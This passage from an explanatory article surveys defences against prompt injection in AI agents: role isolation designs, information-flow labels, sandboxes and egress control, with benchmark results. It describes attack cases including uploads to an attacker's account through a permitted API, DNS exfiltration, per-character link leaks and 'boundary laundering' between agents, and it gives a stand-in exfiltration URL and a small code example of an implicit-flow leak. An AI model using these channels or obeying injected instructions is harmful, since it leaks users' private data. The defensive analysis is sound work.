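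Some tasks require the model to use information from untrusted text. Suppose a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. FIDES can have the quarantined model answer "yes" or "no" to whether there is a request, and a policy can let the privileged model read that answer because a single bit can hardly contain an instruction. FIDES passes the meeting's details to the calendar as a variable. *SPA* (2026), a design for agents that keep working across several requests, similarly makes the quarantined model answer in a predefined format.

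Costa and colleagues label the user's own messages as trusted and public by default, so the reader rule wouldn't protect a name and phone number that the user had typed into the chat. Developers can choose other labels.

### Isolating whole applications

*IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024) divides an agent by application instead of by trust. Each app runs separately with its own language model and memory. A central hub passes requests between the user and the apps, and apps can message each other only through it. The software that relays these messages isn't a language model, so a prompt injection can't take it over.

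In one test, an email contained instructions for the agent to take a sensitive file from the user's cloud drive, send it to the attacker and delete the evidence. The attack worked when all apps shared one context. In IsolateGPT, the email app had to request access to the drive through the hub, and the hub had to prompt the user for permission.

The researchers also ran 1,598 attacks from an extended benchmark, using GPT-4. In the shared version, 20.2% succeeded. In IsolateGPT, 7.6% got as far as a permission request, and each request carried a warning that it might be malicious. The hub can give these warnings because it plans each task before the apps read anything, so it can detect a request that doesn't fit the plan. But the study didn't test how often people would heed the warnings. Yan's participants approved many actions that they had never requested, so the attacks in that 7.6% can't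 be assumed to have failed.

IsolateGPT's separation of apps also doesn't protect against attacks within one app. An email app can read a stranger's message, search the inbox and send a reply without calling another app. IsolateGPT does still ask for approval before irreversible actions such as sending email. CaMeL and FIDES separate reading from acting even when one app does both.

### Results on AgentDojo

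Costa and colleagues tested an ordinary agent and FIDES on AgentDojo, each with and without the policy checks. Both used GPT-4o. The last four columns give utility, the share of legitimate tasks completed, when there was no attack:

| Agent | Policy checks | Successful attacks | Office work | Travel | Banking | Slack |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Ordinary | Off | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
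| Ordinary | On | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES | Off | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES | On | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The attack counts leave out cases that the researchers judged harmless or wrongly scored, such as attacks that the benchmark counted even though a policy had blocked the tool call.

The policy checks stopped every attack even on the ordinary agent. Hiding untrusted text mainly made the checks less disruptive. With the checks on, average utility over the four areas was about 42% for the ordinary agent and 50% for FIDES. Both figures are far below the 84% of an ordinary agent without checks. With OpenAI's reasoning model o1, FIDES's advantage over the ordinary agent grew from 8 to 16 points, because o1 worked better with variables.

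The perfect security score is less impressive than it looks because the researchers knew in advance where the attacks would come from. They labelled a type of data as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. A company labelling its own data wouldn't have a list of the attacks it would face.

*Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) reports that CaMeL completed 67% of tasks on AgentDojo, but it cites an unrelated paper for the figure. Later tests by other groups found lower rates. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on the banking tasks. With its policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed only 37.5% of the tasks, about half as many as with the policies off. In Nikolaou and colleagues' tests with Claude Haiku 4.5, CaMeL completed 49 of 97 harmless tasks. It blocked 26, and the other 22 failed because the plan didn't do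 what the user wanted.

Garby and colleagues analysed how much of the protection comes from separating the roles. They paired each of the 16 banking tasks with nine attacks, giving 144 combinations. In 97 of them, the attack needed a tool that a plan for the user's task would never call, so fixing the plan in advance was generally enough to stop it. In the other 47, the legitimate plan already contained the tools the attacker needed, so those cases, like the one with Bob's address, require labels.

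The evidence from adaptive attacks is encouraging. *AutoDojo* (2026) generated new attacks against CaMeL and DRIFT, another defence that restricts the agent's plan, on several recent models. Most success rates were below 3%, compared with 34.7% for Gemini 2.5 Flash without a defence. The adapted attacks in *The Attacker Moves Second* were far more successful against defences based on filters and training.

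More capable models also lose less utility under CaMeL. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL on 112 industrial maintenance and monitoring tasks that required several agents. CaMeL lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. The tests used CaMeL's separation of roles without data policies, so they leave out the restrictions that halved its utility in banking.

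*ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower than defences that only filter text or add to the prompt. CaMeL's privileged model has to write a whole program, often rewrites it after an error, and calls the quarantined model whenever it needs information from untrusted text. FIDES also needs extra calls to its quarantined model. IsolateGPT added less than 30% to the running time for about three-quarters of queries.

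Willison points out that extracting an address is easier than planning a task, so the quarantined model can be small and might run on the user's own computer. The company that supplies the privileged model would then never receive the user's emails.

### Plans that depend on what the agent reads

A request to do whatever Alice's email says is a problem for role separation too, because the privileged model would have to read the email to plan the task. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) calls this a fundamental limitation of designs that keep planning strictly separate from untrusted data.

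Costa and colleagues classify about a fifth of AgentDojo's tasks as ones where the right sequence of actions depends on the data the agent reads. The share is only 5% in office work but over 40% in banking and Slack, where users ask the agent to pay a bill described in a file or follow instructions on a web page.

A capable model may find a way around the restriction and make the agent vulnerable again. In Garby and colleagues' tests, one banking task told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model never saw the untrusted text, but it wrote a program that read each instruction in the file and called the matching tool, which gave whoever wrote the file control of the tools. Two attacks succeeded this way with CaMeL's policies off.

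Garby and colleagues' own agent, Randori, makes such exceptions explicit. Its plan can "endorse" a particular untrusted value, after which the agent treats it as trusted. The model must choose what to endorse before it reads any untrusted data, and a reviewer can see each endorsement in the plan. Randori completed roughly twice as many banking tasks as CaMeL did with its policies on, and attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay a bill according to a file, and the attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request.

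*Twin Agent* (2026) takes a looser approach. One agent explores the untrusted material and sends short hints to another agent, which can act. The acting agent can adjust its plan as it learns more, and developers can trade usefulness for security by changing the hints' maximum length. The design greatly reduced successful attacks in tests but gives no formal guarantee, since even a short hint could contain an attacker's web address.

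### False content that needs no tool call

Role isolation, like restricted privileges, doesn't stop an attacker from falsifying a summary. The plan runs as intended and every label is correct, even if the quarantined model has written something misleading.

Willison describes a possible leak in which an injection makes the quarantined model encode the private text it has received and tell the user to paste the result into a website in exchange for a funny picture. The user, rather than the agent, sends the data to the website. The agent's rules on who may read data allow it to show users their own data, and none of its rules cover what the user does next.

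Tallam and Miller suggest scanning the agent's answers for suspicious web addresses and instructions before the user sees them. This might catch crude attempts, but it reintroduces a filter that has to recognise malicious text. Clearly marking any passage derived from untrusted sources may be more dependable, since the interpreter already has that information. The user would still have to notice the mark and take it seriously.

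### Leaks that the labels miss

An agent can reveal a secret by what it does as well as by what it sends. Tallam and Miller give the example of a program that leaks a secret number by requesting the same web page that many times. None of the requests contains the secret, but the server's owner can count them in the access log. Errors and delays can give away information in the same way.

One yes-or-no signal reveals little, but a series of them can reveal a whole phone number. A seven-digit number has ten million possible values, and 24 signals are enough to identify it because they can distinguish about 16.8 million (2²⁴).

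Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's labels can miss a signal of this kind even when the program contains an explicit test of the secret. This program, based on their example, reveals whether a bank balance is above a threshold:

```
low  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email(outsider, "Hello")
```

If the balance is high, the third line changes `low` and CaMeL labels it secret. The program then skips the change to `rich` in the fourth line, so `rich` keeps its public label and the email goes out. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. The outsider can tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives, but CaMeL treats the email as a harmless greeting that depends only on a public variable. It misses the leak because it updates a variable's label only when the program changes the variable,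 and here skipping the change to `rich` reveals the balance.

The software around CaMeL's interpreter can also leak data, because it runs the program again after a failure. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so repeated attempts can reveal the secret one bit at a time.

Both leaks are gaps in CaMeL's guarantee, not demonstrated thefts. An outsider can't normally exploit either one directly, because the privileged model writes the program from the user's request alone. They matter most if the attacker can influence that request, for example through text the user pastes into it.

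Costa and colleagues knowingly leave this kind of channel open in FIDES, because closing it completely would mean forbidding almost any action an outsider could observe after the agent has read something private. Garby and colleagues built an interpreter with a stronger guarantee. They proved, with a computer checking every step, that secret data can't affect what an outsider observes except by determining whether the program finishes. The proof holds only if developers label the data correctly and place checks on every tool that can send something out.

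### The work of labelling

Few existing tools supply labels, so developers have to add them. Costa and colleagues wrote software around AgentDojo's tools that labelled each result as the agent received it. They inferred an email's permitted readers from its sender and recipients, although the recipients may have shared it with others. A company document's permitted readers could be taken from the list of people with access, but many companies give staff access to far more files than they need. An agent that follows such a list could send a confidential file to a colleague who should not have access to it.

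Labels that are too broad block legitimate work. In one AgentDojo task, a user wanted a password reset link from the mailbox, but FIDES failed because its labels didn't distinguish trusted senders from untrusted ones. A mail system could often supply that distinction, since it can check whether a message came from the domain in its sender address.

Someone also has to write a policy for each tool and keep it up to date, a burden Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge. Tallam and Miller warn that in an organisation with hundreds of tools, the policies may become inconsistent and hard to review. They recommend rules that apply to many tools, such as one that keeps data within the company's own domain.

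### Several agents that pass each other text

Many products now have an orchestrator, an agent that divides a task among specialised agents. One agent may read a database and another send the messages, which resembles role isolation. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that this separation can fail even when each agent runs CaMeL.

In their demonstration, a user asked for a summary of job applicants' details and wanted it sent to Julie on Slack. The database contained a planted instruction to email the details to an outside address as well:

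1. The database agent retrieved the records. Its privileged model never read them.
2. The orchestrator had its quarantined model summarise the records, and the planted instruction survived in the summary.
3. The orchestrator's program inserted the summary into a request to the notification agent to send it to Julie.
4. The notification agent treated the whole request as coming from its user. Its privileged model read the planted instruction and added an email to the attacker to its plan.

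Each agent followed its own rules, but the attacker's text changed from untrusted data into a trusted request when one agent passed it to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering". They prove that it can happen in any hierarchy of agents where at least one tool returns untrusted data and the agents can include earlier results in their requests to each other.

In multi-CaMeL, each request contains an instruction, which the receiving agent's privileged model reads, and data held in variables, which that model can refer to but not read. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output. The variables keep their labels when they move between agents, so a rule about who may read the data can still apply at the end of the chain.

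The researchers divided AgentDojo's tools among several agents and ran 949 attacked tasks on each of five models. These are the attack success rates:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

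Every attack that succeeded against agents with individual CaMeL used boundary laundering. The benchmark is too easy to show how much multi-CaMeL adds for the newest models, since GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without it. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that stronger, adaptive attacks might still succeed against GPT-5.5. Fable 5's results are also hard to interpret, because it often refused harmless tasks even without an injection. It may have recognised the benchmark as a security test.

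Multi-CaMeL adds protection to CaMeL with little further loss in task completion. On the industrial tasks, it lowered the completion rate by a further 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for the two strongest models.

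## What does a sandbox stop, and what does it leave open?

Rules on tool calls work best when each call does one thing, such as sending an email. Many agents have a tool that runs programs, and a single call can start one that opens thousands of files and contacts any server the computer can reach. Checking only the call would require predicting what the program will do. A sandbox limits what the program can do while it runs, whether the user or a disguised instruction led to the call.

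### Files, credentials and network connections

A sandbox for an agent usually combines three layers:

| Layer | What it does | What a hijacked program can still do |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Process and file isolation | Hides other programs and most files | Send out whatever it can read |
| Removal of credentials | Keeps passwords and access keys outside | Use any access that remains |
| Egress control | Limits which servers the program can contact | Send data to permitted servers |

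Developers usually isolate programs in containers or virtual machines. A container gives a program its own view of files and processes but shares the host computer's kernel, the core of the operating system, so a flaw in the kernel may let the program escape. A virtual machine imitates a whole computer with its own kernel, so it isolates the program more strongly but takes longer to start.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a different design for each of three products. Code that Claude writes on claude.ai runs in a container on Anthropic's servers, behind an extra protective layer, gVisor, and its files last only for the session. Claude Code, an agent for programmers, works on the user's own computer and relies on the operating system's sandboxing features. Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine that can access only Claude's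 settings and the folder the user has chosen. Programmers can often judge whether a command is safe, but most office workers can't, so Cowork needs a boundary that doesn't depend on the user's judgement.

A program in a sandbox can't steal an access key that is kept outside it. In October 2025, Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* described how the cloud version of Claude Code handles the keys for code repositories. The program in the sandbox holds a limited credential that works only with a proxy, an intermediary that passes on network traffic. The proxy checks that the program is sending code to the right place, then attaches the real key. Anthropic's documentation describes a similar option for Claude Code on the user's own computer. Commands receive a placeholder, which is worthless if stolen, and the proxy replaces it with the real key only in requests to hosts the user has listed.

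The local version of Claude Code also uses a proxy to control outbound traffic. On Linux, a sandboxed command can connect only to this proxy, which runs outside the sandbox. The proxy checks each requested hostname against a list of permitted ones, which starts empty.

### Why file isolation alone doesn't prevent theft

File isolation doesn't protect data that is already in the agent's context. Ada Moreno's phone number is part of the conversation, which the model reads outside the container. A hijacked model can write the number into a program that opens `https://pictures.example/?tel=5550142`, and the program doesn't need to read a file. The same applies to emails the agent has already fetched. Egress control can stop the program from sending either.

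Egress control also needs file isolation. Without it, a hijacked command could change a file that the computer runs at the next login, outside the sandbox and with full network access.

By default, commands in Claude Code's sandbox can write to only a few folders but can read almost the whole computer, including files that hold access keys. Unless the user hides those files, the network rules provide most of the protection against theft. The sandbox is also off by default, and if it is turned on but can't start because a component is missing, Claude Code runs the commands without it. Administrators can change these defaults.

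In a February 2026 test at Anthropic without such a boundary, a researcher emailed an employee a prompt to paste into Claude Code. Among routine setup steps, the prompt asked Claude to read the employee's cloud access keys, encode them and send them to an outside server. Claude did so in 24 of 25 repeats. Because the request came from the user, a classifier had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concludes that only egress control and file restrictions reliably stop this kind of attack. The user should probably not be able to override the egress rule, since an employee who pasted in the prompt might also approve the connection.

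Anthropic reports that the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84% in internal use. This is useful because users had been approving about 93% of prompts and paying less attention as the number of prompts grew. But the figure doesn't measure how many thefts the sandbox prevented. Isolation also limits companies' oversight, because their security software can't monitor activity inside Cowork's virtual machine and administrators can retrieve event logs only afterwards.

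### Tools that run outside the sandbox

Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands and the processes they start. The agent's file tools, its web tools and any tool servers on the user's computer run outside it. The sandbox's list of permitted hosts therefore doesn't apply to WebFetch, which opens web pages under separate permission rules. If the sandbox stops a program from sending data, a hijacked model can try to send the same data through WebFetch by putting it in a web address. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, says that web search and page fetching also bypass Cowork's controls on outgoing traffic. It recommends switching off web search unless the user needs it.

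Anthropic originally ran the whole Cowork agent inside a virtual machine, but any failure to start the machine made the product unusable. Now only the code that Claude writes runs there. Anthropic also moved local tool servers out, because they were hard to inspect inside the machine, broke when it changed and sometimes needed other programs on the computer. Anthropic treats them like any other software the user installs. If one of these servers can send email, a hijacked agent can use it to send out data, however tightly the virtual machine confines the code.

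A tool inside the sandbox can also leak data. Tallam and Miller note that if the sandbox permits email, an injected instruction can make the agent send private data in a plausible message. Stopping this requires limiting who the tool can email or labelling the data.

Users of Claude Code can run the entire agent in a container or virtual machine with its own list of permitted hosts. The list applies to the local tools, but it must include the server that runs the model, since the agent can't work without it.

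### Permitted hosts that accept uploads

In October 2025, Johann Rehberger, who writes the security blog Embrace The Red, found that data could leak through the hosts a sandbox is allowed to contact. His post *Claude Pirate* describes the attack on claude.ai, whose code environment could contact only a short list of hosts, mostly for downloading software. The first entry on the list was Anthropic's own API, which also accepts file uploads. The API key in each request determines which account receives the file.

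Rehberger put instructions and a key to his own account into a document. When a user asked Claude to analyse it, Claude saved an earlier conversation to a file and uploaded the file to Rehberger's account. Each upload could hold up to 30 megabytes. The egress control worked as designed and allowed the connection because it went to a permitted host.

Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope, but said five days later that it should not have. In January 2026, two days after Cowork's release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that Cowork had the same flaw. A document with hidden instructions made Cowork upload a user's confidential loan file without asking for approval.

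Anthropic has since added a proxy inside Cowork's virtual machine that inspects traffic to the interface and passes on only requests with that machine's own session token, so it rejects requests with an attacker's key. Rehberger had proposed essentially this rule in October, that the sandbox should let Claude contact only the logged-in user's account. The check has to happen inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other program.

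Anthropic now regards each entry on a sandbox's list of permitted hosts as a "capability grant", which permits everything the host can do. A host where strangers can open accounts is therefore risky even if its owner is honest. Anthropic's documentation warns that permitting github.com, where anyone can create a repository, may allow data to be stolen.

It also warns that the proxy relies on the hostname the program supplies and doesn't normally decrypt the traffic. Because some delivery networks host many sites on the same servers, a program could name a permitted site to the proxy and a different one inside the encrypted request, a technique called domain fronting. A proxy that decrypts the traffic can catch this, but it requires more setup and can read everything the program sends.

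### DNS and shared internal services

The environment where ChatGPT runs Python code had no direct internet access, but it could still look up server names. The security company Check Point Research used these lookups to send out data, as SalesBleed did on Salesforce (*ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel*, 2026). The replies could also carry commands back into the environment.

For a demonstration, Check Point built a custom version of ChatGPT that acted as a personal doctor. A user uploaded laboratory results and described symptoms. The patient's name and the model's medical assessment went to the researchers' server, while ChatGPT told the user it hadn't sent the data anywhere. Check Point says the model treated the environment as unable to send data out, so it gave no warning and didn't ask for approval. OpenAI had already found the underlying problem itself and completed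 a fix on 20 February 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reports no evidence of malicious use.

A sandbox can close this channel by checking a hostname before looking it up, as Claude Code's proxy does. Sandboxed commands can't reach a DNS server directly, and the proxy looks up a name only after confirming that the list allows it. A lookup of `ada-moreno.pictures.example` would never leave the computer.

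Another flaw let data pass between ChatGPT accounts through a service inside OpenAI's network. According to medianet's *Sicherheitslücke in ChatGPT entdeckt* (2026), a German-language report on Check Point's findings, containers obtained software packages from an internal server instead of the internet. Different users' containers could reach the same server, and each could attach notes to a package and read others' notes. An attacker could leave a task in these notes. In one test, the victim's ChatGPT session carried out the task with the victim's permissions, retrieving emails from a connected Gmail account and passing them to the attacker's session.

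OpenAI shut the server down. Check Point says a later break-in at Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, began with the same shared service. TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages* adds that the company expects similar risks on other platforms. Egress rules therefore also need to cover internal services and what containers may write to them. A package server that containers could only read from would have blocked this route.

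### Restricting what the chat page loads

Images in an agent's answer load in the user's browser, outside the sandbox that runs the agent's code. The chat page can restrict them with a content security policy, a setting that the web server sends along with the page. For example:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://images.example`

This policy lets the browser load images only from the page's own server and `images.example`. If the model writes an image address on `pictures.example`, the browser doesn't request it. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* reports that Microsoft used such a policy in May 2023 to block images in Bing Chat, after Rehberger reported a leak. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* argues for placing the main boundary at the outgoing request, because an attacker can word an instruction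 in endless ways but a product needs images from only a few servers.

The policy needs few resources and doesn't depend on the model's judgement, but a permitted server may pass the data on, as in EchoLeak. The page may also have other ways of opening an address. *Check Point Bypassed ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode With a Popup* (Duggan, 2026) reports that a pop-up window escaped the sandbox in which ChatGPT previews web pages, even in Lockdown Mode. In the desktop app, having a conversation was enough to trigger the flaw. OpenAI fixed it on 18 September 2026.

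### Checking the whole address

An agent that browses the web can't work with a short list of allowed hosts. A longer list of reputable sites is more practical, but OpenAI says it isn't enough, because many reputable sites redirect visitors to other addresses and a strict list produces so many false alarms that people learn to click through them. Tenable, a security company, had shown the redirect problem in ChatGPT. ChatGPT's check always accepted bing.com addresses, but Bing's search results use bing.com links that redirect to the sites they list, and an attacker's site can be one of them.

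In January 2026, OpenAI described a check on the complete web address. A crawler, a program that explores the public web, records the addresses it finds and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. The agent may automatically open an address the crawler has already recorded. For any other address, the agent has to find a different source or the user sees a warning. The address `https://pictures.example/?tel=5550142` would fail the check unless it had already appeared on the public web, even if the site's home page passed.

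The check covers page visits in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and searches and page visits in Deep Research. OpenAI runs the small applications that ChatGPT creates in a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and asks for consent. These checks inconvenience some honest sites. According to OpenAI's help page, users have to confirm every link to a site that has opted out of being indexed.

OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak private data through a page's address. A permitted page can still contain false information or new instructions. The agent's choice of which permitted pages to visit can also reveal information.

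### How much a fixed list of pages can leak

After ShadowLeak, OpenAI stopped ChatGPT from adding data to web addresses, so it could open only addresses it had received in full. *ZombieAgent* describes how Radware got around this rule with an email that contained a ready-made address for each letter, each digit and the space. The agent spelled out the stolen text by opening one address per character. Radware reported the attack in September 2025, and OpenAI released a fix on 16 December. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, after the fix ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if the link was in a public index or the user had supplied it in the chat.

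An attacker could still publish many pages and wait for a crawler to find them. If the agent can open any of *M* pages, a request tells the attacker which one it chose. That is at most log₂ *M* bits, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. To identify one secret among *K* equally likely ones, the agent needs *n* requests, where:

$$M^n \geq K \quad\text{or}\quad n \geq \frac{\log_2 K}{\log_2 M}$$

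Suppose the agent can open only 1,024 fixed pages. Since 1,024 is 2¹⁰, each request carries at most 10 bits. A random 16-digit number holds about 53 bits, so the attacker needs at least six requests to get it. If the agent can write its own addresses, it can put all 16 digits in a single address.

| Pages the agent can open | Most bits per request | Requests for a random 16-digit number |
| --- | --- | --- |
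| 10, one per digit | 3.3 | 16 |
| 37, as in ZombieAgent | 5.2 | 11, or 16 if each request stands for one digit |
| 1,024 | 10 | 6 |
| 1,048,576 | 20 | 3 |
| Any address | More than 53 | 1 |

Halving the number of pages on the list cuts the leak by only one bit per request, so a fixed list works best together with a rate limit. If the agent may open only three of the 1,024 pages, it can leak at most 30 bits, which leaves about nine million possible values for the number. The limit has to count requests across sessions, or the attacker could collect the rest the next day.

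Real secrets are often easier to guess than random numbers. The last digit of a payment card number is a check digit, which anyone can calculate from the others. If the attacker also knows the six digits that identify the bank, the remaining nine can be stolen in three requests. Address lists and rate limits protect large amounts of data much better than they protect small secrets. Stealing one 30-megabyte file through the 1,024 pages would take 24 million requests, but the flaw in Claude's file interface let an attacker do it with one upload.

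Rehberger also accepts that an attacker could make each indexed address stand for a letter, according to daily.dev's summary of his post. He suggests storing copies of pages and preventing repeat visits within a session, so that each page can send the attacker at most one signal. This would defeat a scheme with one page per digit, since a 16-digit number always repeats at least one digit. But Radware's attack could already use a separate address for each character at each position. For 16 digits, that takes 160 pages, and the agent doesn't have to open any of them twice.

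These calculations assume that the attacker learns only which pages the agent opened and in what order. The timing of the requests could reveal more. To limit such leaks, Tallam and Miller suggest capping loops whose length depends on a secret, combining repeated calls and making execution times more uniform.

### Sandboxing a browser agent

A browser agent often works in a browser where the user is logged in to email, shops and other sites. Its actions are clicks and keystrokes, which are hard to write rules for because a click at the same point on the screen might open an email or delete it. Blocking an action may not help. In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) stopped an agent from going directly to a website, but it searched for the site and clicked on the result.

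One sandbox design checks the requests that the browser sends. Whatever the agent clicks, placing an order on Amazon requires a particular kind of request to Amazon's server. Each website supplies a list, called an agent sitemap, that matches such requests to actions like "view cart" or "place order". Before the agent starts, a language model reads the user's task and selects from ready-made policies, such as permission to place an order under $50, and the user confirms the choice. A browser extension then enforces the policies and blocks requests to unrelated sites. It can also count requests, so the agent can't get around the $50 limit by placing two orders for $49.

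The researchers tested ceLLMate on GitLab, a site for software projects, with tasks that required commenting on or upvoting a reported issue. The available prompt injections were too weak for a good test, so the researchers wrote 12 scripts that behaved like a fully hijacked agent. ceLLMate blocked all 12 scripts, which tried to steal access tokens, delete projects or give an attacker access, among other things.

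Other tests measured the choice of policies and the cost:

- Three models chose exactly the right policies for 94–100% of tasks, depending on the model and the type of site. On shopping tasks that also required values such as a price limit, they got both right 81–97% of the time.
- Eleven page visits took 13.93 seconds without ceLLMate and 14.94 to 16.02 seconds with it, an increase of 7–15%. The delay grew with the length of the sitemap.
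- The extension used about 25 megabytes of memory.

Blocking all 12 attacks shows that ceLLMate's enforcement works, but every attack needed actions that the policy didn't allow. The agent was still allowed to comment on issues, and ceLLMate doesn't check the content of comments, so an attacker could have the agent post private data in a public one. If the user sends the agent to a site the attacker owns, the policy permits that site, and the agent could send the site anything in its context.

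Writing sitemaps may be a bigger obstacle than the delay. Meng and colleagues wrote theirs for GitLab by hand, covering 51 functions, and someone would have to write and maintain one for every site. An incomplete sitemap adds no protection for the actions it omits. ceLLMate also doesn't check messages sent over WebSockets, the continuous connections that many sites use for live updates.

### Treating the sandbox's output as untrusted

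A sandbox limits what a program can reach, but not what its output contains. The attack on Grok didn't require the program to escape the sandbox, because the decrypted instructions reached the model as the program's output.

Running a program doesn't make its input more trustworthy, so the output of a program that reads a stranger's web page should keep the page's provenance label, as a value computed in CaMeL does. Adversa AI recommends using such labels and checking any tool call whose parameters come from fetched or decrypted content. It also advises companies to watch for the whole sequence of events, because each step can look harmless by itself.

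Anthropic argues that filters should examine tool results as rigorously as web pages. The best time to check for encrypted instructions is after the program has finished and before the model reads its output, because the text that the first filter couldn't read is then in plain language.
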